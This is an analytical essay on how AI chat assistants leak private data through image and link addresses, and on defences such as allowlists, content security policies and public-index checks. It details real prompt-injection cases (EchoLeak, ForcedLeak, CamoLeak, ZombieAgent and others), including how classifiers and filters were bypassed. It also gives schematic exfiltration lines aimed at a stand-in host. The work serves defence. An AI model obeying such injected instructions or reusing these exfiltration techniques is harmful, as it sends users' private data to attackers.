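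Email's defences mostly targeted tracking, and several of them do little against exfiltration. In a chat program, they and two other common proposals would have these effects:

| Defence | Tracking | Exfiltration |
|---|---|---|
| Block images until the reader asks | Prevents it until she loads the picture | Prevents it until she loads the picture |
| Fetch through a proxy | Hides her IP address, device and cookies, but a unique address still shows that an answer included the picture | Doesn't prevent it, since the proxy passes on the full address |
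| Preload through a proxy | In email, also hides whether and when she read the message; in chat, adds little | Doesn't prevent it, and may send the data even if she never looks |
| Block known trackers | Prevents it for servers on the list | Fails if the attacker uses a new server |
| Load only addresses that were already public | Permits it | Limits it, because an address with her private text in it is unlikely to be public |
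| Load only from approved servers | Prevents it by other servers | Prevents it unless an approved server passes the data on |

When Englehardt and colleagues applied two widely used tracker blocklists to newsletters, the number of third parties that received email addresses fell from 99 to 51, and the share of senders that leaked them fell from 19 to 7 percent. But companies that track newsletter readers use the same servers for years, so people can find and list them. An attacker who wants one reader's data can register a new domain that isn't on any list yet.

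Defences can also interfere with each other. A proxy replaces every image address with one on the provider's own server, so a tracker blocker in the reader's browser can no longer identify which company the image comes from. A provider that adds a proxy would have to do any tracker blocking itself.

A proxy and a check for public addresses are a better combination, because the check keeps most private text out of the address and the proxy hides the reader's connection. The owner of a public picture can still learn that somebody's answer included it, and roughly when. If the proxy stores a copy, as Gmail's does, the owner may learn this only once.

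## Loading images only from approved servers

An allowlist names the servers from which a chat program may load images, and the program blocks all others. In the bicycle example, the provider would approve its own image server and little else, so the reader's browser would never contact `pictures.example`, even if the model wrote the image code.

### Two ways to apply the list

A provider can apply the list with an output filter, a part of the chat software that searches the model's text before display and removes image codes with unapproved addresses. It can also use a content security policy, which the browser enforces. The site sends the policy along with the page, and the browser checks each request against it before sending anything. A short policy for a chat page might read:

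```
Content-Security-Policy: default-src 'self'; img-src 'self' data: https://images.chat.example
```

The "img-src" part is the allowlist for images, and it permits the chat site itself ('self'), images embedded in the page (data:) and one other server. The "default-src" part limits most other kinds of content, such as scripts, fonts and frames, to the chat site. The developer's blog loke.dev recommends a similar policy for AI chat pages, with one named storage server for images.

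Under this policy, the browser sends nothing to `pictures.example`, and the reader sees at most a label or a broken-image icon. But the policy doesn't stop a link from opening when she clicks it, and it doesn't apply to requests between servers.

A filter has to recognize every way of embedding an image, which many of the mail programs in the Efail tests failed to do. A content security policy is more reliable because the browser checks each image request, however the page makes it. But the policy only works where a browser displays the answer. A phone app that displays answers without a browser needs its own check, which ChatGPT's phone apps lacked for some time after the website had one.

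### The first fixes

Microsoft introduced an early policy of this kind for Bing Chat in 2023. According to Embrace The Red, the approved servers included www.bing.com, the search engine's main address. Three years later, other researchers used the same address to get data out of another Microsoft product.

GitHub Copilot Chat, an assistant for programmers, had the same flaw as Bing Chat. In Embrace The Red's *GitHub Copilot Chat*, Rehberger describes how a comment in a source file made the assistant put codes and names from the chat into an image address. He reported this in February 2024 and received confirmation of a fix on 12 June. It seemed to him that the assistant no longer displayed Markdown images at all, but Willison wrote in *GitHub Copilot Chat* that GitHub had disabled only images from untrusted domains.

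Later evidence fits Willison's account better. Microsoft's *VS Code*, a security advisory for the code editor in which the assistant runs, shows that the editor's chat features still relied on a list of trusted domains in 2025. According to the developers' statement, which FreeBSD (2025) reproduces, the advisory concerned a mistake in how the editor handled wildcard patterns in that list, so a specially written address could pass as trusted.

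Such mistakes are easy to make. For instance, a check that accepts any address beginning with `https://chat.example` would also accept `https://chat.example.attacker.example`, which belongs to someone else. Microsoft corrected the error in May 2025 with version 1.100.1, which also stopped the editor's chat from loading remote images.

Even if the software reads the list correctly, an allowlist works only if requests to approved servers cannot reach an attacker. Since 2025, security researchers have found several products in which they could.

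### EchoLeak

Microsoft 365 Copilot answers questions about a company's material by searching the user's email, files and Teams chats and adding whatever seems relevant to the model's context. In January 2025 Aim Labs, a security research group, told Microsoft that an outsider could steal material from that context by sending the user one email. Microsoft deployed a fix in May, and the public learned of the flaw, CVE-2025-32711, on 11 June (Reddy and Gujral, *EchoLeak*, 2025).

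*Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025) is the fullest account, and it comes from those who found the vulnerability. It describes an attack that had to get past several defences in turn.

Microsoft first ran incoming text through a classifier, a program trained to detect prompt injection and keep it from the model. Aim Labs got past it by writing the email as if its instructions were for the employee who received it, with no mention of AI or Copilot. Ravia attributes the miss to a shortage of good training data, but the task is also hard because many ordinary work emails ask someone to compile information, and a classifier that blocked them all would make Copilot useless.

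Copilot also had to retrieve the email when the user asked about something else. Search systems often split long texts into pieces and retrieve those closest in meaning to the question. Aim Labs wrote one very long email that repeated the same instructions under many headings, such as onboarding, HR questions and leaves of absence, so that a question about any of these could bring the instructions into Copilot's context. This was partly guesswork, because Microsoft doesn't publish the details of its search, but in tests Copilot retrieved the email for a variety of topics.

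The instructions told the model to take the most sensitive information in its context and put it in a web address. Copilot had an output filter that removed Markdown links and images with outside addresses. The filter recognized the usual form, in which the address follows directly after the label. It missed the variant from Pandoc's manual, where the address has its own line:

```
![Project plan][1]

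[1]: https://pictures.example/dot.png?note=(private text)
```

Aim Labs first used this gap to get a link past the filter, but the victim would have had to click it. The filter also missed an image, which needed no click. The renderer built an image tag, and the browser got ready to send the request.

The attack failed here because Copilot's content security policy didn't include the attacker's server, so the researchers looked through the servers it did include. The list in Ravia's account has 29 different entries, and about half appear twice, so it seems nobody had checked it carefully. Eleven entries begin with an asterisk, which stands for any subdomain. One of these covered all of SharePoint, Microsoft's service for company websites, where every customer gets a subdomain, so an attacker could get an approved subdomain by becoming a customer.

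Having a site on an approved domain wasn't enough, because SharePoint no longer let customers run their own code on its servers. But the researchers found a SharePoint function that would fetch an outside address on request. It worked only if the victim had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site, which few people would do. They kept looking and found a similar function in Teams that required no invitation. In schematic form, the final image address had a second address inside it:

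```
https://preview.approved.example/fetch?url=https://pictures.example/(private text)
```

The browser followed Microsoft's policy when it sent a request to Teams. A Microsoft server then requested the inner address, delivering the private text to the attacker. Teams acted much like Gmail's image proxy, which also passes on the full address.

Copilot normally cites the sources for its answers, which might have revealed the email. But the email contained an instruction to its "recipient" never to refer to it, for compliance reasons, and Copilot followed that instruction.

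Ravia calls EchoLeak the first zero-click attack on a major AI application. Images had been leaking chat data without a click since 2023, but in those attacks the victims had pasted in the hostile text or pointed the chatbot at a page that contained it. In EchoLeak, the attacker only had to email an employee and wait for them to ask Copilot a question. Microsoft said that no customers were affected. Reddy and Gujral report that Copilot has since begun to strip reference-style links and embedded images from incoming external content. This change addresses the filter's mistake, which was separate from the problem with the approved servers.

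### A trusted domain for five dollars

Companies use Salesforce to keep records of their customers and sales. Its Agentforce product adds AI agents that can search those records. Many companies also put a Salesforce form on their website, where anyone can submit contact details and a message, and Salesforce saves each submission as a record. The security firm Noma found that an outsider could use the form to plant instructions for the agents, an attack it named ForcedLeak.

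When an employee later asked Agentforce to deal with the submission, the agent carried out both the employee's request and the planted instructions. Security Affairs' *ForcedLeak flaw in Salesforce Agentforce exposes CRM data via Prompt Injection* reproduces those instructions, which were to provide the email addresses of sales leads and then a "preview image", labeled as a customer logo, with those addresses in its URL.

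Agentforce's content security policy allowed the image's domain, my-salesforce-cms.com, but the domain's registration had expired. According to Hackread's *ForcedLeak Flaw in Salesforce Agentforce AI Agent Exposed CRM Data*, anyone could buy it for $5. Salesforce Ben quotes Noma as saying this had created "a trusted exfiltration channel".

EchoLeak needed an approved server that would forward a request, while in ForcedLeak the attacker owned the approved server. An allowlist contains names, and the software that checks it doesn't verify who currently owns them. Salesforce may have controlled the domain when it wrote the policy, but somebody had to keep paying for it or delete the entry when the company stopped.

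Noma reported the flaw on 28 July 2025. The Hacker News (2025) gives its severity as 9.4 on CVSS, a common scale from 0 to 10. Salesforce recovered the domain, and on 8 September began to enforce a list of trusted addresses for its AI agents' output. This list is also an allowlist, so someone will need to check that its entries still belong to the right people.

### SearchLeak

*SearchLeak*, published by the security firm Varonis in June 2026, describes another leak from Microsoft 365 Copilot, this time from the part that searches a company's emails, calendars and files. The attack began with a link to Microsoft's real website. The link's address contained a question, and when the victim opened it, Copilot answered using the victim's access to company data. One click delivered the question, so the attacker didn't need to plant text in an email or a web page. The Hacker News (2026) notes that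 ordinary anti-phishing tools were unlikely to flag a link to a genuine Microsoft domain.

In the demonstration, Copilot was asked to find an email and put its subject line in an image's address. A subject line is short, but it sometimes contains a login code.

Copilot had a filter that wrapped answers containing HTML in a code block, so that the browser would display an image tag as text instead of loading the image. But the filter ran only after the model had finished writing, while the browser rendered the answer as it arrived. The browser therefore requested the image as soon as it received the tag. The filter then turned the tag into text, so the finished answer looked as if the defence had worked.

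The content security policy was in force from the start and would have blocked a direct request to the attacker's server. However, it allowed requests to all of Bing, which can search for pictures similar to one whose address the user supplies. Bing's server has to fetch that picture to run the search. Varonis wrote a Bing address that contained a second address, which pointed to Varonis's own server and included the subject line. When the browser requested the Bing address, Bing's server requested the second one and so sent the subject line to Varonis.

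Bing was already on the list of approved servers that Aim Labs had gone through the year before. When Microsoft fixed EchoLeak, it evidently didn't remove every approved server that would fetch an outside address, or stop those servers from doing so for Copilot. Nobody seems to have reported whether the Bing function would have worked in 2025, or in 2023, when the same host was on Bing Chat's list.

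Microsoft classed the flaw, CVE-2026-42824, as critical but scored its severity at only 6.5, while the US National Vulnerability Database gave it 7.5. Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers, and Varonis presented no evidence that anyone had used it in a real attack.

Varonis advises companies to clean an answer as they render it, and to check for approved servers that fetch addresses supplied by users. A provider has to do both. Cleaning the answer during rendering would have stopped this image tag, but it wouldn't have helped against EchoLeak, where the filter didn't recognize the code at all.

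### GitHub's signed addresses

GitHub, a site where programmers store and discuss code, had anticipated the relay problem. Its content security policy lets browsers load images only from domains that GitHub owns. Images from elsewhere go through a proxy called Camo. According to GitHub's documentation, Camo hides the reader's browser details from other users.

Camo fetches an image only if the address it receives includes a valid cryptographic signature, which only GitHub can compute. Without this requirement, Camo would be as useful to an attacker as the Teams function. When someone publishes text with an outside image, GitHub replaces the image's address with a signed Camo address. A model that writes private text into an address can't compute the signature Camo needs to fetch it.

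In June 2025 Omer Mayraz, a researcher at Legit Security, found a way to leak data using only addresses that GitHub had already signed. The firm's *CamoLeak* explains that anyone can send text to GitHub through its programming interface and get back signed addresses for the images in it. Mayraz obtained a signed address for each letter and symbol he might need, each leading to an invisible one-pixel picture on his own server.

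He put this alphabet, with instructions, in a hidden comment on a pull request, which is a proposed change to a project's code. The instructions applied to any user who opened the pull request and asked GitHub Copilot Chat about it. The assistant had the same access as that user, including to private projects. It looked up the private text and spelled it out in pictures, one for each character. Camo fetched each picture from Mayraz's server, so he could read the text from the requests. He also had the model add a random number to each address so that a stored copy of the picture wouldn't prevent a new request.

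With *N* signed addresses to choose from, *n* images can carry at most

$$n \times \log_2 N\ \text{bits}$$

For *N* = 64, each image carries 6 bits, as much as a single character in an address that the model can write freely. Sending the 1,500 bytes that fit in one long address would therefore take 2,000 images. But a 40-character access key would take only 40 images, and the images are invisible. In his tests, Mayraz extracted the description of an undisclosed security flaw from a private project, and the results of a search for an access key.

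The signature proved only that GitHub had created the address. Signing each address separately can't show whether an attacker chose which addresses to load and in what order. The tracking example is the same attack with only two pictures, one for readers who had mentioned an illness and one for everyone else.

Legit Security reports that GitHub turned off images in Copilot Chat completely and gave 14 August 2025 as the date of the fix. OECD's *GitHub Copilot Chat Vulnerability Exposes Private Code and Secrets* (2025), an entry in a database of AI incidents, lists the first news coverage on 8 October. The entry treats the harm as having occurred, but SecurityWeek's *GitHub Copilot Chat Flaw Leaked Data From Private Repositories* and Legit Security describe only Mayraz's own tests.

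GitHub has also used a less strict fix. According to an undated summary from its bug-bounty program, copied on the Vulners page *GitHub*, it fixed a Copilot leak by loading images only from trusted domains and adding warnings about links.

### Which servers are safe to approve?

The address in an image request may contain private text, so a provider has to consider everything an approved server might do with that address. The server might fetch another address, as Teams and Bing did, or keep the text where an outsider can read it later.

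Superhuman, an email program with an AI assistant, had a policy that allowed images from docs.google.com, which also hosts Google Forms. A Google Form can be submitted just by requesting a web address that contains the answers. The security firm PromptArmor created a form and sent a test user an email with hidden instructions. When the user asked for a summary of recent mail, the assistant wrote code for an image, using the form's address with the contents of other emails filled in as answers. No image came back, but Google stored the text in PromptArmor's form.

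Willison (2026) reports in *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* that the leak covered dozens of emails, including financial, legal and medical ones, and credits Superhuman with treating it as urgent. In April 2026, PromptArmor reported a similar leak from OpenAI's Codex, again through an image request that filled in a Google Form. OpenAI has fixed that leak.

An approved server can also redirect the browser to another address. Under the web standard, browsers check the new address against the content security policy too, so a redirect to an unapproved server fails. An output filter can't catch the redirect because it checks only the address in the text. An image proxy may also follow redirects itself, outside the browser's control. After finding a leak in the AI features of Notion, a program for notes and documents, PromptArmor advised the company to ensure that nobody could use its image server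 this way.

Even a server that only serves images keeps logs, which are harmless if only the chat provider can read them. But if a policy approves every subdomain of a company that rents out storage, an attacker can rent some, point the image at it, and read the private text in their account's logs.

An approved server is therefore safe only if it doesn't redirect, fetch, store or log for outsiders. The provider also has to keep control of the domain, as ForcedLeak showed. If outsiders can add pictures to the server and see when people load them, Mayraz's alphabet will also work there.

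trackr.live's *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data* argues that approval should take in the server's name, the path (the part of the address after the name) and the owner. A content security policy can contain paths, so a provider could approve a folder of generated pictures on a server and leave out its other functions. Browsers ignore the path after a redirect, however, so this only helps if no approved server will redirect to the functions that the provider meant to exclude.

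By this standard, Microsoft's list for Copilot was far too broad. It included a search engine, a chat service and a website host, all of which do much more than serve images. A provider would do better to keep generated images on a separate server used only for that purpose, and approve that server by its full name.

### What an allowlist still prevents

Published cases can make allowlists look less effective than they are, because researchers write up the attacks that worked and nobody counts the ones a policy stopped. The researchers who found EchoLeak, SearchLeak and the GitHub attack report that a content security policy blocked images from the attacker's server, so they had to find a flaw in a particular company's services, which Ravia describes as tedious. The attacks on Continue, Dify and HuggingChat required no such search because they could load an image from any server.

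An allowlist also makes repairs simpler. Once Microsoft knew about the Teams function, it could close that route on its own servers, without retraining a model or asking customers to install anything. The attacker then has to find another relay, which is easier when the list has 29 entries and many of them cover whole families of servers.

Providers can find out what a strict list would break before they impose it. Browsers support a report-only mode, which loads everything as usual but reports each request that the policy would have blocked. The reports may show that a chat page needs only two or three image servers. After the policy takes effect, similar reports can alert the provider to a possible attack, such as a sudden run of blocked requests to an unknown server.

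An image allowlist does not stop data from leaving by other routes. In August 2026 Microsoft patched CoSnitch, a set of flaws that Varonis had found in the personal version of Copilot. As Hexnode describes it, a link again started the attack, but the data could leave through Copilot's tool for fetching web pages. Microsoft's servers run that tool, so a policy in the reader's browser has no effect on it, and the tool would need its own allowlist.

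The strict list also blocks images that would help the reader who wanted advice on touring bicycles, such as a photograph from a manufacturer's website, along with the attacker's pixel. The provider can't approve the manufacturer's server without checking how it handles requests and who can read its logs, and the provider can't check every website with a picture of a bicycle.

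## Checking each address against a public index

A provider that can't vet every server can vet individual addresses instead. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) describes how ChatGPT does this. OpenAI builds an index using a crawler, a program that visits public web pages and records the addresses it finds. The crawler has no access to users' conversations or accounts. Before ChatGPT automatically loads a page or an image, it looks for that exact address in the index and loads it if it's there. If not, ChatGPT either has the model try a different website or shows the reader a warning that the link is unverified and may include information from their conversation.

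A photograph on the manufacturer's website has probably been public for months, so the crawler has recorded its address and the image loads. The model composed the address of the attacker's pixel from the reader's details during the chat, so the crawler can't have recorded it and the pixel doesn't load.

Requiring an exact match also stops most of the tricks that got past allowlists. EchoLeak, SearchLeak and the Google Forms leaks all needed an approved server to accept an address with private text after the server's name. A public index may contain thousands of Bing addresses, but it is very unlikely to contain one that includes the subject line of the reader's latest email. OpenAI objects to lists of trusted sites because many such sites redirect visitors elsewhere. Under the new rule, a redirect does less harm because the redirecting server receives only a public address, with no private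 text to pass on.

The rule blocks some harmless pictures. The crawler won't have seen a photograph that the manufacturer uploaded this morning, or one on a company's internal website. Some sites add an expiring code to each image address, so the address the crawler recorded last week differs from today's. The provider also needs an index that covers much of the web. OpenAI has one, but a small firm that builds a chatbot on Dify probably doesn't.

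### What OpenAI guarantees

OpenAI says the rule should keep the model from "quietly leaking user-specific data through the URL itself". The rule doesn't guarantee that a page is trustworthy or free of harmful instructions, or that a site won't try to manipulate the reader. It blocks one way for data to leak but does nothing to stop prompt injection.

The guarantee relies on timing. If an address was on the public web before the conversation began, nobody can have composed it from that conversation's secrets. OpenAI says, a little more cautiously, that a public address is "much less likely" to contain the user's private data. A crawler might, for instance, have found a link to someone's medical file that was never meant to be public, but that link was already exposed before the conversation.

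The argument holds for the text of the address, but the model's choice among public addresses can also carry information, as its choice among signed addresses did in Mayraz's attack on GitHub.

Suppose the owner of `pictures.example` publishes 365 pictures of bicycles, one for each day of the year, and waits for the crawler to find them. The hidden text under the bicycle review contains an instruction for the model to show the pictures for the day the reader leaves home and the day she returns. Both addresses are in the index, so the pictures load. The owner sees requests for 3 June and 24 June and learns when her house will be empty, although neither address mentions her.

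OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) calls the mechanism Safe Url and describes its purpose more broadly, as detecting when information from the conversation would reach a third party. A check against a public index can't detect every such case. In the example, the dates reach a third party even though the address passes the check.

### How much a choice can carry

Each choice among the 365 pictures carries at most about 8.5 bits, by the same formula as for Mayraz's alphabet. Even this small amount can matter because many secrets are short.

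Take a six-digit login code. It has a million possible values, so it contains

$$\log_2 10^6 \approx 19.9\ \text{bits}$$

Suppose the attacker has 36 pictures in the index, one for each letter and digit. If the requests arrive in order and the model can reuse pictures, *k* loads can encode 36 to the power *k* different messages. Three loads allow 46,656 messages, which is too few, but four allow 1,679,616, which is enough for any code.

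Things get harder for the attacker if the order is lost and the chat program blocks repeats. He then learns only which pictures loaded, and the number of different sets is

$$\binom{36}{k} = \frac{36!}{k!\,(36-k)!}$$

Five pictures give 376,992 possible sets and six give 1,947,792, so he needs six loads. With 1,024 pictures in the index, two loads are enough if their order counts, because they can form 1,048,576 sequences (1,024 squared).

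The last column of this table gives the number of loads needed to send 1,500 bytes, which a single freely composed address can carry:

| Public addresses | Six-digit code, order kept, repeats allowed | Six-digit code, order lost, repeats blocked | 1,500 bytes, order kept, repeats allowed |
|---|---|---|---|
| 36 | 4 loads | 6 loads | 2,322 loads |
| 1,024 | 2 loads | 3 loads | 1,200 loads |

These are minimums, and a real attack would probably need more loads. To send a code in four loads, for example, the model has to convert it from base 10 to base 36 without a mistake. The public-index rule is a large improvement because it makes sending out a long conversation or the contents of an inbox impractical, but a login code, a diagnosis or a pair of dates still fits in a few images.

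### The earlier check, url_safe

OpenAI's first check on image addresses, called url_safe and introduced in December 2023, had trouble with the same trick. Before showing an image, the ChatGPT website sent the address to OpenAI's server, which labeled it safe or unsafe. OpenAI didn't say how the server decided, so outsiders could only learn about url_safe by trying addresses, whereas anyone can read a website's content security policy.

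On the day he noticed the check, Rehberger tried 36 images, one for each letter and digit. According to Embrace The Red, nine of them loaded. The image for "a" passed but the one for "d" didn't, for no reason he could see. He still sent the word "hi" to his server. Nine images are also enough to send a login code, since seven loads in order give almost 4.8 million combinations.

Later tests in Imperva's *From ChatBot To SpyBot* showed that url_safe accepted any address that already appeared in text from the user, including the standing preferences ChatGPT calls custom instructions. This was presumably because the model can't have added a secret to an address that was there before. But an attacker who gets text into those instructions can include an address for each character. The check also accepted fragments, so an attacker could cover the whole alphabet with one long address by cutting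 it off at a different point for each letter. It accepted most bare domain names too, and an attacker could register one per character for a dollar or two each. Imperva still thought OpenAI was moving in the right direction, because extracting a lot of data undetected had become much harder.

For some domains, url_safe didn't require a known address. Rehberger found that it trusted windows.net, where Microsoft rents out storage, so he could rent storage there and read private text from ChatGPT in its logs. On his blog, Embrace The Red, he lists apache.org as another trusted domain whose logs he could inspect. He reported both to OpenAI in October 2024, and asked the company to publish its list of trusted domains.

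*HackedGPT* (2025), by the security firm Tenable, describes a more instructive case involving Bing. The check always passed addresses on bing.com, and Bing gives each search result a fixed address there that redirects to the actual website. Adding text to such an address breaks it. Tenable therefore got Bing to index one test page for each letter of the alphabet, and had ChatGPT spell out private data in images that used the matching Bing addresses. Tenable reported the problem in December 2024, and it was still unresolved when the firm published its advisory, *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* (2025).

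That attack relied on a domain that url_safe trusted too much, and the present rule uses OpenAI's index, not Bing's. But the attack is still the best available evidence of how hard it is for an outsider to get a page for each letter of the alphabet into a public index, and it suggests that this isn't very hard.

Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* reports that OpenAI strengthened url_safe around August 2025, which stopped the attacks Rehberger had shown by then. *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*, the technical paper OpenAI released with the new rule, points out that an attacker can still use one address per letter. Rehberger thinks this isn't much of an obstacle for anyone with a large blog, who probably has 36 indexed addresses already. A more ambitious attacker could use thousands, each standing for a whole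 word.

### Spelling with web pages

Three well-documented attacks of this kind mainly involve pages that the model fetches, rather than images in the answer. As with CoSnitch, the provider's servers send the request, so no browser policy can block it and the attacker doesn't get the reader's IP address. The arithmetic is the same, though, and the vendors' fixes resemble the rule for images.

*Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection* (Schwartzman, 2024) describes an attack on ChatGPT from when it would open only addresses that appeared in the user's prompt. The attack starts when a user pastes in a long piece of code without noticing the instructions inside. In the simple version, the instructions list one address for each age range and tell ChatGPT to open the one that matches the user's age. Even if the user hasn't stated an age, ChatGPT can infer the range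 from a remark about finishing high school that day.

ChatGPT also accepted a shortened form of any address in the prompt, so Schwartzman could send longer numbers by encoding each digit in the number of characters the model kept. ChatGPT wouldn't open the same address twice, probably because it had stored the page, so he supplied a separate address for each digit. The model counted characters poorly, and he had to add a short program to do it. ChatGPT opened at most ten addresses per prompt, which limited the attack to ten characters. Ten digits hold about 33 bits, enough for a postal code or a phone number.

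OpenAI judged his report "non applicable". By September 2025, ChatGPT was opening addresses only exactly as given, which rules out the shortened ones. But Rehberger believes ChatGPT still treats an address in the user's message as safe for the rest of the chat. If pasted text counts as part of the message, an attacker who can hide a list of addresses in something the user pastes doesn't need to get them into an index.

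The exact-address restriction came after an attack called ShadowLeak, in which the security firm Radware got ChatGPT's research agent to add an employee's name and address to a link. Goodin (2026) explains in *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack as a vicious cycle in AI* that OpenAI responded by forbidding ChatGPT to add anything to a web address. Radware then supplied web addresses that were already complete.

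Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes the resulting attack. The attacker sends the user an email containing hidden instructions and a separate web address for each letter, each digit and the space. When the user asks ChatGPT to do something with her Gmail account, ChatGPT reads the attacker's email, finds the private data and opens the matching address for each character. Requests can arrive out of order, so Radware also made a separate set of addresses for each position, with one address for "a" in first place and another for "a" in second place. Ten positions take 360 addresses for the letters and digits. Radware also got a version with Markdown images to work, but found it less reliable and easier to block.

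Radware reported the flaw on 26 September 2025, and OpenAI fixed it on 16 December. According to Goodin, ChatGPT now opens a link from an email only if the link is in a well-known public index or the user provided it. OpenAI announced nearly the same rule for ChatGPT in general six weeks later. The email rule stops ZombieAgent as Radware built it, because nobody had indexed the addresses it used. An attacker who gets 360 pages indexed beforehand would presumably get past the rule.

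Anthropic's Claude reads web pages with a tool called web_fetch, whose original rule was also strict. Willison (2026) explains in *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets* that the tool could open only addresses that the user had typed or that Claude's search tool had returned. The one exception was links on pages it had already fetched, and in July 2026 Ayush Paul published an attack that used this exception.

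Paul built a website that showed ordinary visitors nothing suspicious. When Claude visited, the site claimed that AI assistants had to prove who they were working for by finding their user's profile, one letter at a time. Each page linked to a page for every possible next letter, so the order of the letters was clear. Claude spelled out the user's name, employer and home city. The user had never told Claude the city, but dyb's *The Read-Only Lie* reports that Claude inferred it from the name of a high school hackathon. Each page offered 27 links, so each choice sent 4.75 bits. By dyb's calculation, about 30 choices sent roughly 143 bits, or less than 18 bytes.

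Anthropic said it had already found the problem internally and didn't pay Paul a bounty. It has since stopped web_fetch from following links on the pages it fetches. Claude can still choose among search results, but an attacker has much less control over which pages those are. A public-index rule would also have made Paul's site harder to use, because all its branching pages would have had to be in the index before Claude visited.

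### Making the alphabet harder to use

Rehberger suggests two ways to slow such attacks. ChatGPT could store each response for a few minutes, so that repeat visits to an address wouldn't send new requests, or it could refuse to visit an address twice in one session. He hadn't tested whether ChatGPT already did either. Schwartzman's results suggest that in 2024 it did something similar for web pages, and Tenable noticed the same behavior in its tests.

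Blocking repeats does little to protect short secrets. If the requests still arrive in order, 36 pictures allow 36 × 35 × 34 × 33 = 1,413,720 sequences of four with no repeats, so four loads are still enough to send a login code. If the order is also lost, it takes six. Radware's numbered addresses get around both problems. With a picture for each digit in each of six positions, 60 in all, the model can send any six-digit code in six loads, without repeats and in any order.

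These measures do limit how much an attacker can learn. If order is lost and each picture can load only once, he learns only whether each picture loaded. With 36 pictures, he can get at most 36 bits in a session, not quite enough for two login codes. Sending more would require a larger collection of indexed pages, which would take him more time and make him easier to notice.

A limit on the number of images per answer, which Rehberger proposed in 2023, would probably help more. With three images and an alphabet of 36 pictures, the attacker can't get a whole login code in one answer, but he can narrow it from a million possibilities to about 21. With an alphabet of 1,024 pictures, he would get the whole code. The limit would also have to apply across a session, or the model could send the rest in its next answer.

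The provider could also watch for suspicious patterns of requests. dyb points out that Paul's attack made about 30 requests in a row to one site, each for an address one character longer than the last. Some ordinary browsing looks similar, such as reading a long manual page by page, so a detector would need further signs, like unusual speed. An attacker who knew about the detector could use addresses that don't follow a pattern.

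A more thorough remedy for images is for the provider to save a copy of each picture when its crawler visits the address, and show readers that copy. The picture's owner would then receive no request when the answer appears, so he couldn't track the reader or learn anything from the model's choice of picture. The copy has to be made during the crawler's visit because a proxy like Gmail's still makes one request when a reader first needs the picture. Storing so many pictures would be expensive, some would be out of date, and their owners might object to the copying. OpenAI describes loading the image from its public address and doesn't say that it shows saved copies.

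Rehberger's last concern is that a check protects only the products that use it, and some of OpenAI's developers may not know it exists. Previously, url_safe was missing from the phone apps and the Mac app for some time. In March 2026 OpenAI listed the places where Safe Url applies, including its Atlas browser and its Deep Research feature, and said that Canvas and ChatGPT Apps take a similar approach.

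PromptArmor found that OpenAI's log viewer, where developers read the logs of their own AI applications, displayed Markdown images insecurely. A developer might have blocked images in the application itself, so that a malicious image didn't load for the customer. But if someone flagged the answer for review, the image loaded when the developer opened the log, and the request sent out the customer's data.

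## Should remote images be off by default?

A chat program can't always tell a manufacturer's photograph from an attacker's pixel, but it can leave both unloaded until the reader asks for them. Classic Outlook still treats pictures in email that way. Chat programs differ, and most of them use one of these settings:

- No remote images. The answer contains only text and embedded pictures.
- Placeholders. Each outside picture appears as an empty box, and the program fetches the picture if the reader clicks.
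- Provider-hosted images only. Pictures load automatically from the provider's own servers and from nowhere else.
- Automatic loading with an optional strict mode. Outside pictures load without a click, perhaps after a check, unless the reader or an administrator has switched on something stricter.

A chat interface contacts an outside server without a click only when it loads outside images automatically. Images from the provider's own servers don't cause this, so the provider can keep outside images off by default and still show its own.

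### What current products do

GitHub turned images off completely in Copilot Chat after Mayraz's attack. JetBrains, which makes programming tools, blocks them in its AI Assistant and shows "image-fetching blocked for security reasons" instead. In *AI Assistant*, a question on the JetBrains support forum, Menci asks how to fix this.

Gemini doesn't show images from outside servers. Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (2025) describes an output filter that finds external image URLs and doesn't render them. Tenable's *The Trifecta* supports this, reporting that markup for such images no longer worked in Gemini and that the firm's researchers had to get data out through Gemini's web browsing tool instead. But Google hasn't applied the rule to all its products. *Faking the Pipeline* (Odson and Morris, 2026) describes a leak from Google's coding tool Antigravity,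 which still displayed images in the chat.

OpenClaw, an open-source AI agent, comes close to allowing only provider-hosted images. According to its *Security model*, OpenClaw's control page loads only images from its own server, embedded images, and profile pictures from GitHub and Gravatar. The browser blocks all others before sending a request.

The coding assistant Continue has used placeholders, or something like them, since VerSprite reported its leak in 2025, and Claude did so earlier. Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed* describes how Anthropic responded within two weeks to a July 2023 report by making users click "Show Image" before a picture loaded. Rehberger didn't think the fix was perfect, but it stopped the automatic leak. Claude's iPhone app needed a separate fix, which a researcher quoted by Willison (2024) announced in December 2024.

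Claude's current setting is harder to classify. According to Anthropic's *Enabling and using web search*, Claude picks images from Bing's search results and displays them next to its text, each with a link to the original page. The images have no separate switch, so a reader who doesn't want them has to turn off web search. The page doesn't specify whether the browser gets the images from Anthropic, Microsoft or the original website, or whether "Show Image" still applies when Claude writes image code itself.

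ChatGPT loads external images automatically if their addresses are in OpenAI's public index, and offers a strict setting called Lockdown Mode. In open-source programs, the strict setting is often up to whoever installs them. LibreChat is a chat program that organizations can run themselves. According to its *HTTP Security Headers*, its content security policy is off by default so that administrators can check what it would break. Turning it on only starts report-only mode, which blocks nothing, and the administrator has to change a second setting to enforce the policy. If they mistype that setting's value, the policy stays in report-only mode. Until the administrator enforces the policy, the browser will load any image that the program doesn't remove itself. Dify also had no content security policy by default when veganmosfet tested it in December 2025.

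A setting that turns off remote images also has to cover pictures outside the assistant's answers. OSV's *PYSEC-2026-2738*, a security advisory about the chat program Open WebUI, describes how any logged-in user could point a profile picture at an outside address. Everyone who viewed the picture then sent that address a request. The same method worked with hidden images in shared chats and notes.

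### The argument, premise by premise

The case for keeping outside pictures off by default has five premises:

1. Outsiders can influence the image addresses in an answer.
2. Loading an image gives its server the address and details of the reader's connection.
3. The model's context often contains private data.
4. Checks on addresses don't stop every leak.
5. Automatic display is worth less to readers than the harm they can expect from it.

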